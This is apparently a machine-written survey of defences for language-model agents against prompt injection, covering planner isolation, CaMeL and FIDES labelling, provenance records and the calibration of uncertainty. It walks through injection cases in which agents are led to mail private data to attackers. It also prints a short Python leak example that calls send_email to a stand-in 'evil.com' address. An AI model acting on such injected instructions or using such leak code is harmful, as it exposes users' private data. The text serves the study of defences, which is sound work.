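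### What isolation gains and costs

A plan written in advance can be useful even when nobody attacks. Before the plan runs, a program can check that it contains no payment or deletion. A person could check too, but the screen plans average 213 lines of code, and few users would read that much.

The main drawback is that the planner depends completely on descriptions. An ordinary orchestrator may notice that two reports conflict, or that a result makes no sense, and investigate. A planner that finishes before the first screenshot has to anticipate every such problem and write a response to it. Such a plan can easily hide uncertainty. In the plan for the natural-products task, if the system cannot tell whether a click on a cookie notice worked, the program treats the click as a success.

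Isolation would also be less valuable if models could resist injections on their own. Seip and colleagues ran ten of their hardest attacks against Claude Opus 5 with Anthropic's standard safeguards but no isolation. It resisted all ten and completed every task. Claude Sonnet 5 fell for two, both times sending a sales report to someone impersonating a colleague.

Ten attacks are too few to show that Opus 5 is safe. A model that failed 26% of the time would still pass all ten about once in twenty tries. Isolating the planner keeps injections from adding steps to the plan, however persuasive they are, which no test of a model's resistance can guarantee. But if the plan for the sales report took the recipient's address from the email itself, a false address could cause the same mistake without adding a step.

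### When the content decides what to do

Isolating the planner works worst when the task depends on what the agent finds. *Trident* (2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to deal with a caterer's email. The email might contain an invoice, a question about allergies, or both, so the planner cannot list the steps without learning something about what it says.

*Trident* tested CaMeL, the text-based system that Foerster and colleagues built on, on 45 tasks, nearly all of this kind. With GPT-4.1 and no attacks, CaMeL completed 7% of runs, compared with about 86% for an unprotected agent. No attack succeeded against CaMeL. The unprotected agent completed only 20% of runs under attack, so leaving the planner exposed was not a good alternative.

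CaMeL also failed for reasons other than its fixed plan. Of its 1,215 runs with GPT-4.1, including those under attack, 574 failed because a security rule blocked a legitimate action that relied on untrusted data. A looser rule would have allowed more of these actions, but also more false values. In another 377 runs, the quarantined model failed to extract what the plan needed.

According to *Twin Agent* (2026), letting the reading model pass more information to the planner increases the risk, but letting it pass too little makes the agent less useful. *Trident* proposes a system that measures this information in bits. A choice among *k* options counts as log₂ *k* bits, so picking one of ten shirts or none would count as log₂ 11, or about 3.5 bits. If the planner can receive at most *B* bits in total, and everything else stays the same, an attacker can choose among at most 2^*B* courses of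 action.

In practice this limit is very loose. A typical run used at least 24 bits, 19 for answers and 5 for reports on whether steps had succeeded, and 24 bits can distinguish almost 17 million possibilities. Even one bit can allow harm if one of the two branches it selects between is harmful. In the tests the limit was set so high that it never took effect, so the protection came from hiding the text from the planner, restricting the permitted actions and asking the user to approve exceptions.

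With those measures, the system completed 54% to 74% of runs under attack, depending on the model. No attack succeeded if the user rejected every request that showed the attacker's action, but 3% to 5% succeeded if the user approved everything. On the 18 tasks where the content determined which actions to take, the system completed 22% to 41% of runs under attack.

Some requests depend even more on the content. If a user says "Do what Jane's email says", no rule can always separate what the user wants from what an attacker has added, because the email determines the task. Seip and colleagues' system sends such requests back and asks the user to be more specific.

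## How can each claim keep a record of where it came from?

An isolated planner can still send a sales report to an attacker if it takes the address from an untrusted email. Provenance is the record of which source a value came from and what happened to it on the way. A program can use this record to restrict how a value is used, for example by refusing to send private files to an address found in a stranger's email. A person or another model can use it to go back to the email and check whether a claim is true.

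A program needs very little information to restrict how a claim is used. It can block the report using only a record that the address came from an outsider, even if it can't determine whether the address is wrong. Checking whether a claim is true requires a pointer to the exact place it came from and access to that place.

### Labels that travel with the data

Security engineers have restricted the use of data in this way since the 1970s, under the name information-flow control. Every value carries a label, which *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) describes as recording who may observe the data and which sources influenced it.

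A value computed from several inputs gets the strictest combination of their labels. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give the example of two documents, one that A, B and C may read and one that B, C and D may read. Only B and C may read a text derived from both. *APPA* (2026) writes the rule as

(*R*, *t*) ∧ (*R*′, *t*′) = (*R* ∩ *R*′, min(*t*, *t*′))

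where *R* is the set of permitted readers and *t* is a level of trust. Before each action, a program compares the labels with a policy. Costa and colleagues use two main policies. A consequential action, such as a payment, goes ahead only if the decision to take it and the values it uses are trusted. A message goes out only if everyone who will receive it is a permitted reader of its contents.

Suppose Alice asks her agent to answer a stranger's email, and a quarantined model drafts the reply from the email and her private notes. A hidden instruction could put the notes into the reply, so the program tracks the following labels:

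| Text | Permitted readers | Trusted |
|---|---|---|
| Alice's notes | Alice | Yes |
| The stranger's email | Alice and the stranger | No |
| The draft reply | Alice | No |

The stranger is not a permitted reader of the draft, so the program refuses to send it, without having to detect the hidden instruction. But it would also refuse to send "Thanks, I'll reply next week", because the label depends on what the model received, not what it wrote. Dongol proves that an agent of this kind is secure however the quarantined model behaves, but points out that this is only because it refuses harmless replies too. The protection fails if the stranger can see the refused message, for instance in an error log.

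A plan that didn't need the notes could avoid the problem by giving the model only the email. The stranger would then be allowed to read the reply.

### Labels have to follow decisions

Suppose the plan has the quarantined model answer a yes-or-no question and sends the stranger "1" for yes or "0" for no. Neither digit is private, so both messages pass the check. But a hidden instruction can make the answer depend on Alice's notes, such as whether she is looking for a new job, and the stranger can then learn this from the digit. Dongol proves that labels allow this kind of leak if they track data but not decisions. To prevent it, a system has to give everything that happens inside a branch the label of the condition that selected the branch. CaMeL, a labelling system from Google DeepMind, has a strict mode designed to do this, but Dongol analyses only its normal mode.

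It is easy to get this wrong. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found that CaMeL can leak a secret through a branch the program does not take. They adapted an example from the 1970s, which works roughly like this:

```
rich = True
flag = True
if balance > threshold:
    flag = False
if flag:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
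```

If the balance is above the threshold, the program sets `flag` to False and labels it private. It then skips the line that would change `rich`, so `rich` keeps its public label and the program sends the email. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes False and the program doesn't send the email. The attacker learns whether the balance was above the threshold, although the program never used a value labelled private to decide whether to send the email.

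The standard remedy is to stop the program when a private condition is about to change a public variable, here at the line that changes `flag`. Stopping also leaks information, because the program stops only when the balance is high. Most systems accept this leak of one bit per run. CaMeL, however, runs its programs inside a retry loop that does not track labels, so repeated runs could reveal a whole secret one bit at a time. Both faults are gaps in CaMeL's guarantee, but an attacker would have trouble exploiting them because the planner writes its program without reading untrusted text.

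If an agent makes a payment because of something in a stranger's email, the decision to pay is untrusted even if the user supplied the amount and the recipient. FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, therefore labels the choice to call a tool separately from the values the tool receives. It is not designed to stop the agent's choice of tools from revealing private information. Costa and colleagues argue that preventing such leaks would in effect forbid any publicly visible action once the agent had read anything private.

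### CaMeL and FIDES

CaMeL adds labels to the dual-LLM pattern. As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) describe in *CaMeLoT*, the planner writes a program in a restricted form of Python, and an interpreter runs it and labels each value with its sources and permitted readers. Before each tool call, a short policy function checks the labels and allows or denies the call.

In one of their examples, the program reads a chat channel, has the quarantined model find Bob's email address in the messages, and sends "Meeting at 3pm" to that address. The steps are what the user wanted, but anyone in the channel could have posted a false address. A policy that accepts only trusted recipients blocks the message. Nikolaou and colleagues add a check that can find some such violations before the program runs, so that an agent doesn't fail at the last step of a long task. The planner receives the sequence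 of steps that would break the policy and can repair its plan.

In FIDES, the planner works one step at a time and reads trusted results directly. If part of a result is untrusted, the program stores that part and shows the planner only a name for it. The planner can read the stored text, but the whole conversation then becomes untrusted, and the policies block many later actions. For a task such as adding a meeting to the calendar if an email requests one, FIDES can let the planner read a yes-or-no answer without triggering these restrictions, because one bit is unlikely to carry an instruction.

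Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks with office software, travel booking, banking and the messaging service Slack. They left out the yes-or-no feature because few of the tasks needed it. Against an ordinary GPT-4o planner, 152 attacks succeeded. None succeeded against FIDES with its policies switched on, or against the ordinary planner with the same policies. The two differed in how many tasks they could still complete when nobody attacked:

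| Planner | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no policies | 75% | 70% | 99% | 93% |
| Ordinary, with policies | 37% | 73% | 38% | 20% |
| FIDES, with policies | 59% | 41% | 53% | 48% |

The ordinary planner averaged 84% without the policies and 42% with them. FIDES averaged 50% with the policies, so it recovered only about a fifth of that loss. With the policies off, FIDES averaged 61%, so most of its shortfall from 84% came from hiding text from the planner. A stronger planner may handle hidden text better. With o1, a reasoning model from 2024, FIDES's lead over the ordinary planner when both use the policies grew from 8 points to 16.

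The attacks all failed partly because the researchers labeled a field as untrusted if any attack in AgentDojo used it. This fairly tests whether the policies work when the labels are right, but a company would have to label its data without knowing where attacks will come from.

Later tests of CaMeL also found strong security but a large drop in completed tasks. Garby and colleagues ran it on AgentDojo's banking tasks with two models. Without policy checks, it completed 67% of the tasks with GPT-5.2 and 71% with MiMo-v2.5. With the checks, it completed 37.5% with either model. The checks stopped every attack, but only 5 of 622 attacks had succeeded without them. In about two thirds of the test cases, the attack needed an action that CaMeL's plan would never contain, so the fixed plan was enough to stop it. The checks would probably matter more in a test with more attacks that supply false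 values. A system in *Language-Based Agent Control* had a similar drop on the Slack tasks, from 15 of 21 completed to 8. CaMeL completed 7 under the same conditions.

CaMeL's drawbacks are greater with small models. *CapLite* (Xu, Liu and Nakayama, 2026) tested CaMeL with 15 open-weight models, most of them small enough to run on a personal computer. Only 20 of 13,935 attacks succeeded. But CaMeL completed 25% of tasks when there was no attack, compared with 59% for an unprotected agent, and used about 94,000 tokens per task instead of 28,000. Many of the models could not reliably write a program that ran, and one failed 68% of the time.

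Another defence, Progent, has the model write its own list of permitted actions, and Progent let 676 attacks through. So an agent that relies on a weak model tends to fail at its task if the model has to write the program, and to be unsafe if the model has to write the permissions.

CapLite uses a much simpler form of provenance. A recipient, an amount or anything else that determines whom or what an action affects must appear in the user's own request. If the recipient's name appears only in an email, the agent asks the user. No attack succeeded, and CapLite completed 28% of tasks, using about 17,000 tokens per task. The rule does not cover the body of a message, so an attacker can still influence what the agent writes to the right person.

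### What the proofs guarantee

Garby and colleagues also designed a programming language for agents. They gave a computer-checked proof that every program in it, including any that a model writes while the agent is running, has a property called noninterference. This means that if two runs start with different private data but are otherwise the same, someone who sees only the public output cannot tell them apart, except by whether they finish.

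Language models choose their words partly at random, so the theorem compares the two runs' output probabilities. The statistical distance between them is at most the average of the two runs' chances of not finishing. If one run fails to finish 2% of the time and the other 4%, the distance is at most 0.03.

Real tasks often need an exception. If a user asks an agent to pay the bill in a file, the account number has to come from the file, which is untrusted. The language therefore lets a program endorse a value, or mark it as trusted. Garby and colleagues prove that endorsement cannot expose private data, whatever the attacker has written, but it can still let a false account number through.

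Their agent completed 65% to 75% of the banking tasks, depending on the model, and 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both cases, the user had asked the agent to follow the payment instructions in a text file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. When the researchers turned off endorsement for two of the models, the completion rate fell by 10 to 13 percentage points. Turning off endorsement also blocks this attack, because the agent can no longer pay anyone named only in a file.

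Noninterference is too strict for some useful agents. An assistant that sends Alice's availability to anyone who requests a meeting reveals private data by design. Dongol instead compares an agent with an imaginary one that has the same plan and policies but never obeys an injected instruction. The real agent is secure if it leaks only what the imaginary one could also leak. By this standard, the meeting assistant may send the calendar but not a password reset code. An agent that refuses every action also passes, so engineers have to measure usefulness separately. The proofs cover leaks but not other harm, such as the agent following an injected instruction to delete a file.

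Labels also have to stay attached to data when one agent gives work to another. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three agents that each ran CaMeL without additional policies, and asked them to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. The applicant database contained a hidden instruction. The orchestrator pasted the summary, which carried that instruction, into its request to a notification agent. The notification agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so it sent the summary to Julie and also emailed it to the attacker. Each agent had followed its own plan, but the attacker's text became a trusted instruction when the orchestrator passed it on. Garby and colleagues found a smaller version of this fault inside CaMeL, where inserting an untrusted value into a piece of text could make it trusted.

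Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed the problem by sending instructions and data separately, so that the data keeps its labels. On their benchmark, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% when CaMeL protected each agent separately, and 0.0% with the fix. The fix made little difference to the average because the benchmark rarely exposed this weakness. Agents also completed fewer tasks with the fix, though the drop was small for the strongest models.

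### Records that let someone check a claim

An evidence record links each claim to a quotation, a line in a file, a region of an image or a moment in a recording, so that someone can check whether the claim is right. A program can use a simple label to identify that a date came from a video, but the label doesn't help anyone check the date.

Ma, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *Omni-Decision*, built a planner that works from such records. The system answers questions that require video, audio, web pages and calculation. Perception tools describe the media in text, and the planner works from a ledger, which at step *t* is

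*S*ₜ = {*U*ₜ, *F*ₜ, *E*ₜ, *C*ₜ}

*U* lists what the system still needs to find out, *F* holds the facts and calculations the answer depends on, *E* holds confirmed evidence with its source and time, and *C* holds unresolved conflicts.

In one example, the system had to work out how many days separated two scenes in a travel video. The ledger began with a list of the information needed, including both dates. A tool then found a title card reading "Fiji Islands, South Pacific, Oct 26th", and the ledger stored the text with the time it was on screen, 2:18 to 2:31. The system later correctly answered 81 days.

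The planner cannot write to the ledger directly. A critic, another language model call, compares each new result with the open needs, and ordinary code then updates the ledger. When two sources disagree, the ledger keeps both claims, and the conflict normally blocks a final answer until the system resolves it. In one task, a video gave a date only to the month while a web source gave an exact day. The ledger recorded the mismatch, whereas a prose summary could have kept only one of the dates.

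The system answered 81.4% of 360 questions correctly with the ledger, 68.3% with a running summary instead, and 60.3% with the raw history. The 13-point lead over the summary can't all be due to the links to sources, because the ledger also adds a checklist, a critic and a rule for when to stop.

Ma and colleagues then replaced one part of the system at a time with a weaker model from the Qwen3.5 family. Replacing the planner lowered the score by 23.3 points, and replacing the perception model lowered it by 15.8. They conclude that planning is the main bottleneck. The comparison isn't quite even, because the original planner and perception model came from different companies, and one replacement may have been a bigger step down than the other. The planning model also serves as the critic and writes the final answer, so replacing it probably made the system worse at those jobs too. With the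 strongest planner in place, problems with perception and web searches caused about three quarters of the 67 remaining failures.

Like the planner, the critic reads only text. If a perception tool misread "Oct 26th" as "Oct 28th", the critic could accept the wrong date and store it with the correct video timestamp. The record would still help someone check the date by opening the video at 2:18.

### Depending less on intermediaries

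A claim often passes through several agents before anyone acts on it, and any of them can get it wrong. Someone who can open the source does not have to rely on those agents.

Lumbroso (2026) makes a more general argument of this kind in *Cybernetic and Epistemic*. An agent that needs only its supervisor's approval learns what the supervisor will accept, which may differ from what the task requires. In a chain of agents, these differences can add up without anyone noticing. A retrievable record makes the chain less dependent on each agent's word, if nobody has altered the record and someone can check the claims in it.

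In Lumbroso's example, a coding agent reports that it resolved a conflict between two versions of a file by keeping the newer one. The report is more useful if the agent adds that the older version still referred to a part of the program that no longer exists. A reviewer can look for that reference in the older version, and if it isn't there, the agent's reason was wrong.

Most of Lumbroso's cases come from one person's projects, with no comparison group, and the paper presents them only as illustrations. The experiments it cites are stronger evidence. Bansal and others found in 2021 that explanations made people more likely to accept an AI's recommendation whether or not it was correct. In a 2025 experiment by Kim and others, explanations also increased reliance on both right and wrong answers, but people were better at telling them apart when they had a source to check or noticed an inconsistency.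 Models may benefit in the same way, since Wang and Mannby's aggregators stopped making errors once they received the original source.

### Where provenance stops helping

A claim can be false even when the record of its source is correct. A shop's database is a trusted source for the colour of a shirt, but it can be wrong. An attacker can replace the contents of a file that the user has told the agent to follow, as in the two successful attacks on Garby and colleagues' agent. Wang and Mannby's orchestrator sometimes adopted a forged claim even after the subagent had reported a problem with the record.

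Free-text summaries cause a different problem for labels because they mix sources. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) notes that a model's context may combine text from many sources, which makes it hard to decide which parts to label separately. A summary of nine company documents and one public web page is only as trusted as the web page, and only people allowed to read all ten sources may read it. In a long session, almost everything can end up untrusted. Context compaction would make this worse. If a summary mixed the user's standing rules with web text, the rules would become untrusted too, unless the program stored them separately.

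One remedy is to find out which inputs influenced a response. Costa and colleagues describe a method that identifies those messages and regenerates the response from them alone, so the response needs only their labels. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests labels that estimate how much each source contributed, which would allow more actions but give up the certainty of a strict rule. It also suggests having a person authorize exceptions.

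Evidence records may also go unread. Coding agents that knew where to find their full saved history did not complete their tasks any better than agents without it. Ordinary code can check some links automatically, for example by confirming that a quotation appears in the file a report cites. This would catch an invented quotation, but not a genuine quotation from a forged file, or one that leaves out an exception in the next sentence.

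## How can a description say how sure it is, and when should the planner look again?

A link to the exact second of a video lets someone check a date. The description also has to show how likely the date is to be right, so the planner can tell whether it needs checking.

### Formats for passing on doubt

Engineers who built speech and language systems faced this problem decades ago. A speech recognizer can hardly tell "recognize speech" from "wreck a nice beach" by sound alone. If it passed on only its best guess, a translation program that used the text would receive no sign of the other candidate. Many recognizers therefore passed on an n-best list, a ranking of whole transcripts with scores, and a later component that had more information about grammar or the topic chose among them. Some language-processing pipelines did the same with alternative parses of a sentence.

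A lattice stores the alternatives more compactly, as a network in which every link is a word with a score and every path is a possible transcript. If ten places in a sentence each have two candidate words, the 20 links for those words cover 1,024 transcripts. But every later component must be able to search a lattice, whereas any program can read a plain sentence.

A describing model has similar options. For the glass of clear liquid on the counter, they might look like this:

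| Format | What the planner receives | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| Ranked readings | Water 0.9, cleaning fluid 0.1 | Combinations multiply as objects are added |
| Confidence per claim | "The glass contains water" (0.9) | Drops the links between claims |
| Set of possible answers | Water or cleaning fluid | Needs labelled examples, and gives no ranking |
| "Not observed" | Contents not visible | Someone has to ask about each fact |

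Whether claims depend on each other can matter. Suppose a robot's data show that exactly one of two glasses holds water, but not which one. A confidence of 0.5 for each glass is correct, but a planner that treated the claims as independent would calculate a 25% chance that both glasses hold water.

Explicitly labeling a fact "not observed" is useful because many planners treat any fact missing from their record as false. Without that label, such a planner would assume that a skateboard the camera missed isn't there.

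*Bridging Learned Visual Perception and Symbolic Belief-Space Planning via Probabilistic Grounding* (Azran, Navat and Keren, 2026) combines a confidence per claim with a "not observed" answer. The system asks a vision-language model one question per fact, such as whether a cabinet is open, and reads the probabilities the model gives to "true", "false" and "null". If "null" is the most likely answer, the system keeps its earlier estimate. Otherwise, it multiplies the old odds by the new ones, so two readings of 80%, each with odds of 4 to 1, give odds of 16 to 1, or 94%. It then collects the most likely states of the room until their total probability reaches a chosen threshold, and searches for a single plan that works in all of them. For example, when the robot couldn't see a bowl, it opened the cabinet first, which works whether or not the bowl is inside.

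In simulated homes, the system completed 87% of simple tasks, 57% of medium ones and 67% of hard ones. When the same vision model gave a single true-or-false answer per fact, the success rates were 40%, 21% and 0%. These percentages are rough because they appear to come from about 15, 14 and 9 trials. On medium and hard tasks, the two versions produced a valid first plan equally often, so the system's advantage there must have come later, perhaps because it updated its estimates instead of starting again from each new image. However, the system needs a separate model call for every fact, and these calls took up most of the running time.

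Shi and colleagues argue that a confidence score still isn't enough, because the planner can't tell from it whether to ask the user, search again or try another tool. They propose giving the planner some of the describing model's internal activations. In a small test with Qwen-1.5B, these activations contained more information about the model's uncertainty than its answer, a score or a written explanation did. But the test defined uncertainty by how much the model's repeated answers varied, and a model can give the same wrong answer every time. Also, a planner built by another company usually couldn't use the activations.

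### How rewriting removes doubt

Words such as "probably" are the easiest format to use, since every language model can read and write them, but they are easily lost when a model rewrites the text. In *From 'May' to 'Is'*, Belem, Wu and colleagues (2026) had five models rewrite single sentences from scientific papers and radiology reports. Depending on the model, 30% to 49% of the rewritten sentences sounded more or less certain than the original. Most models were 1.5 to 2 times as likely to raise the certainty as to lower it. In one case, a radiologist had listed a lung disease as one possible explanation for a feature on an X-ray, and the paraphrase gave it as the explanation.

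The effect can build up with repeated paraphrasing. Claude Haiku 4.5 made 20% of the medical sentences sound more certain after one paraphrase and 40% after five, which is a bad sign for agents that repeatedly compact their history. Changing the prompt reduced the problem but did not remove it. The exact rates are uncertain because a language model judged which sentence sounded more certain, and people often disagree about this.

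Doubt expressed in conversational language may be especially easy to lose when text is shortened. *Effects of Transcript Compression on LLM-based Medical Misinformation Detection* (2026) reports that shortening transcripts of Japanese health videos tended to remove conversational hedges, while formal ones were more likely to remain.

A confidence level is safer as a number in its own field than as a word in a sentence, because ordinary code can copy the number from one record to the next, much as pinning copies a user's rules.

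### Conformal prediction

Conformal prediction turns a model's scores into a set of possible answers that contains the right one at a chosen rate. It does not require the model's own probabilities to be accurate. Suppose engineers want a robot's list of possible liquids to omit the right one at most 10% of the time:

1. They collect 99 photos of glasses whose contents they know, taken in the kind of kitchen where the robot will work.
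2. They give each photo a score, which is 1 minus the probability the model assigned to the correct label. A high score means that the model did badly.
3. They sort the scores and take the 90th smallest as the threshold. The general rule for *n* cases and an error target *ε* is to round (*n* + 1)(1 − *ε*) up to a whole number, and here 100 × 0.9 = 90.
4. For a new photo, they score every possible label in the same way, and each label that scores at or below the threshold enters the set.

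This works because the new photo comes from the same source as the other 99. The score of its correct label is equally likely to have any rank among the 100 scores, so it has a 90% chance of being among the lowest 90.

If the model gives water a probability of 0.9 and cleaning fluid 0.1, their scores are 0.1 and 0.9. With a threshold of 0.93, both labels enter the set, so the robot must check. With a threshold of 0.6, only water enters.

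A 10% error rate is much too high for this robot, which should serve the glass only if it is more than 99.8% sure. A 0.2% target requires at least 499 calibration cases. With exactly 499, the threshold is the worst score, so one strange photo can determine it. With fewer, the threshold's required rank exceeds the number of scores, so every set includes every label.

The guarantee is also an average over all glasses. Suppose the set contains a single label only 10% of the time, and all the errors fall in those cases. Then a single-label set is wrong 2% of the time, ten times the target, and the robot doesn't check in those cases. *A Gentle Introduction to Conformal Prediction and Distribution-Free Uncertainty Quantification* (2021) explains that researchers have proved no method can promise the chosen rate for each kind of case without further assumptions about the data. The true coverage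 also depends on which calibration photos happen to be chosen. With 99 photos, it varies around 90% with a standard deviation of about 3 points.

Coverage can fail altogether if the new photos come from somewhere else, such as a kitchen with dimmer lights. Some versions of the method correct for known kinds of change. But the calibration photos don't show how the model responds to an image that an attacker has altered to make it confidently wrong.

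### Calibrating the choice or the description

Two papers from Princeton, one of them written with Google DeepMind, applied this method to different halves of a robot.

*Robots That Ask For Help* (Ren, Dixit and colleagues, 2023) calibrates the planner with conformal prediction. A language model proposes several next steps and scores each one, and conformal prediction selects the steps that remain plausible. If more than one remains, the robot asks a person. For example, if the robot is told to put "the bowl" in the microwave and there is a metal bowl and a plastic one, it should ask which. In an office kitchen, with a target of 85%, the planner chose correctly in 87% of trials and asked for help in 67%. Without help, it chose correctly in 62%. A weaker planner, GPT-3.5, also met the target, with 87% correct, but needed help in 86% of trials.

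The guarantee depends on the planner receiving a correct description of the objects, which Ren and colleagues call the method's primary limitation. If a captioning model had described the metal bowl as plastic, the planner could be sure of its choice and still damage the microwave.

*Perceive With Confidence* (Dixit, Mei and colleagues, 2024) calibrated the perception system instead. A vision model drew boxes around chairs, and the researchers measured how much they had to enlarge the boxes in each calibration room to enclose the chairs completely. They required this to hold from every sampled position in the room. For a target of 85%, the margin was 0.73 metres.

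Averaging over positions gave a margin of 0.02 metres, which was far too small. A planner steers the robot to new places, where the vision model may see chairs from unfamiliar angles and make more mistakes than average. In 30 real room layouts, a four-legged robot with a margin of 0.73 metres avoided collisions 90% of the time. With the smaller margin, it mistook part of a chair for free space in every trial and hit a chair in half of them. The larger margin could block many paths, but the robot kept only the area where boxes from successive views overlapped, so the boxes shrank quickly. The method assumes that nothing in the room moves except the robot.

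### Can a planner trust the stated confidence?

Recent studies suggest that a model's confidence can be right on average but give a planner little information about a particular case. If nine in ten glasses held water, a describing model that reported a 90% chance of water for every glass would be perfectly calibrated, but the planner couldn't use that number to work out which glasses were empty.

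Yang, Han and colleagues (2026), in *The Mirage of Calibrated Confidence*, found something close to this in small vision-language models. They replaced a model's written account of what it saw in an image with a different one, and measured whether its stated confidence changed. The confidence barely changed in about 40% of cases for Qwen3-VL-4B, and in 82% to 90% for a version that other researchers had trained to be better calibrated. The models also often wrote phrases like "let me recheck", but their confidence did not systematically fall afterwards. These results come from models with 4 billion parameters and mostly from visual mathematics problems, so they may not hold for current frontier models or for photos of kitchens.

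*VL-Calibration* (2026) trains a model to report one confidence in what it saw and another in its reasoning. Its premise is that a model's general knowledge can hide doubt about the image. Separate scores would help a planner if the method works, because only doubt about the image is a reason to take another photo.

More encouragingly, *Confidence Calibration in Vision-Language-Action Models* (2025) found fairly low calibration error in several settings for models that turn images and instructions directly into robot movements. The error varied with the model, the task and how far the robot had got through the task. Poor average calibration is also easy to correct with labelled data. In *Calibrate-Then-Act*, Ding, Tomlin and Durrett (2026) compared a language model's stated confidence with how often it had been right at each level, and adjusted the figures to match. The average gap between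 confidence and accuracy on a set of factual questions fell from 0.618 to 0.029. But this correction cannot separate good readings from bad ones if the model reports the same confidence for both.

### Do planners act on doubt?

A planner also has to use the confidence it receives. Shi and colleagues found that adding an uncertainty signal to an earlier component's output reduced overconfidence in every recipient model they tested.

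Ding and colleagues used a puzzle in which one of several boxes holds a prize. The model can guess at any time or open boxes to check them first, but each check shrinks the prize by a fixed proportion. If a check leaves 80% of the prize, the best strategy is to guess once one box is more than 80% likely, and otherwise to check the likeliest box. Even Qwen3-8B, a small reasoning model, could follow this strategy when the prompt contained the probabilities. On tasks closer to real work, such as reading a data file in an unknown format, models did not find the right balance between checking and guessing on their own, even after training. Giving them estimated probabilities helped.

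Evidence is mixed on whether models act on their own doubts. *Causal Evidence that Language Models use Confidence to Drive Behavior* (2026) finds that confidence influences whether a model declines to answer a question. But Okcu, Wang and colleagues (2026) found in *The belief-action gap in language model agents* that, in simple grid worlds, changes in an agent's beliefs did not consistently explain changes in its preferred action. Models can also be too cautious. *Language models seek help despite guaranteed score losses in question answering* (2026) reports that they ask for help even when doing so is guaranteed to lower their score.

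For a few dangerous actions, it may be safer to have ordinary code compare the stated probability with a fixed threshold. *Uncertainty Quantification for LLM Agents* (2026) points out that a calibrated risk does not by itself determine the right action, so someone would still have to set the threshold based on the stakes.

### What another look is worth

The value of looking again is

(expected value of the best action after looking) − (expected value of the best action now) − (cost of looking)

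Suppose a subagent tells a coding agent that a file is a duplicate, and the report has a 95% chance of being right. Deleting a duplicate has a value of 1, deleting the only copy has a value of −50, and leaving the file alone has a value of 0. Deleting the file without checking has an expected value of 0.95 × 1 − 0.05 × 50 = −1.55, so if the agent can't check, it should leave the file alone. Now suppose it can compare the files, which always reveals whether the file is a duplicate but lowers the value by 0.1. If it compares them and deletes only a duplicate, the expected value is 0.95 − 0.1 = 0.85, so it should compare them first.

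With a good backup, the penalty for a wrong deletion might be only 1. Deleting now would then be worth 0.95 − 0.05 = 0.90, more than the 0.85 from looking first, so the planner should delete without looking, even though it is just as unsure as before.

An unreliable look is worth less. With the original stakes, suppose the comparison gives the right answer only 80% of the time. The agent would delete the file only after a second "duplicate", and the value of looking falls to

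0.95 × 0.8 × 1 − 0.05 × 0.2 × 50 − 0.1 = 0.16

Agents can also look too often. In an example from *Verifiable Hidden Dynamics Play* (2026), an agent had to choose among 14 options and pay to inspect each one. It found the best option, worth 93.29, within the first few inspections, but went on to inspect all 14 at a total cost of 134 and ended with −40.71. After training, the agent stopped after eight inspections that cost 27, chose the same option and ended with 66.29. When an agent looks by asking the user a question, it uses up some of the user's patience, which *Value of Information* (2026) weighs against the expected gain from the answer.

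In theory, free information never hurts a single decision maker, who can always ignore it. *Seen Is Set in Stone* (2026) tests agents in invented worlds where looking itself has consequences. When deciding whether to look, a language-model planner should also weigh the risk of reading an attacker's instructions.

### Looking after something goes wrong

Pchelintsev, Patratskiy and colleagues (2025), in *LERa*, built a system that looks again after a robot's action fails. A vision-language model receives a camera image and the failed action, describes the scene and suggests causes. In a further step it explains how to correct the plan, and then it writes the new plan. The researchers tested this in two simulated households where they had changed the state of some objects, such as leaving a microwave open, and on a simulated table where a robot arm sometimes dropped blocks. The table shows the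 share of tasks completed:

| Setting | No replanning | Replanning without an image | LERa |
|---|---|---|---|
| VirtualHome | 50% | 50% | 94% |
| ALFRED, unfamiliar rooms | 32% | 43% | 54% |
| Table, GPT-4o | 19% | 75% | 67% |
| Table, Gemini | 19% | 72% | 86% |

Half of the VirtualHome tasks were unchanged, so a planner that learned only that an action had failed apparently recovered in none of the others. It could not tell, for example, that the microwave was already open. In the tabletop tasks, knowing that the last action had failed was usually enough, since the planner often had to pick up the block again. With GPT-4o, the success rate was actually lower when the planner also had the image.

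Describing the scene before replanning also helped. The model completed 93% of the VirtualHome tasks when it described the scene and then replanned, without the explaining step, but only 52% when it received the image and had to write a new plan in a single step.

The system relies on a separate failure detector. In ALFRED's unfamiliar rooms, its success rate fell from 36% when the detector was wrong 5% of the time to 21% when it was wrong 15% of the time. Without replanning, the corresponding success rates were lower, at 25% and 13%.

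On a real robot arm, LERa replanned successfully in 15 of 18 trials. In one trial, the user asked the robot to remove the apple, but the object detector had labelled a green pear as an apple. The gripper failed to lift the pear but turned it slightly, and the model recognized in the new image that it was not an apple. If the gripper had worked, the robot would have removed the pear without detecting the mistake. A system that looks again only after failures would also miss the mistake when a robot serves a glass of cleaning fluid, because serving it triggers no error message.

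### When a second describing model helps

Instead of looking again itself, a planner could ask a second model to describe the same photo. Suppose each model mislabels 10% of glasses, there are only two possible labels, and their errors have a correlation of *ρ*. The chance that both are wrong is

0.1² + *ρ* × 0.1 × 0.9 = 0.01 + 0.09*ρ*

| Correlation of errors | Models disagree | Wrong when they agree |
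|---|---|---|
| 0 | 18% | 1.2% |
| 0.5 | 9% | 6.0% |
| 0.8 | 3.6% | 8.5% |
| 1 | Never | 10% |

If two models' errors are independent, agreement between them cuts the risk of error from 10% to about 1%. At a correlation of 0.5, most of that benefit disappears, and the models also disagree half as often, so the planner gets fewer warnings. Two independent models that agree are still not reliable enough for the glass of water. Three would be, with an error rate of about 0.14%, but only if their errors were independent.

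Different models' errors are often not independent. In *Hidden Clones*, Bugaud (2026) tested 17 vision-language models from eight families and found that they provided only as much variety as 2.5 to 3.6 independent voters. On 1.5% to 6.5% of questions, the majority was wrong even though the best model was right. *The Visual Insensitivity Gap* (2026) gives examples in which three separately trained models ignored the relevant part of an image and confidently gave the same wrong answer.

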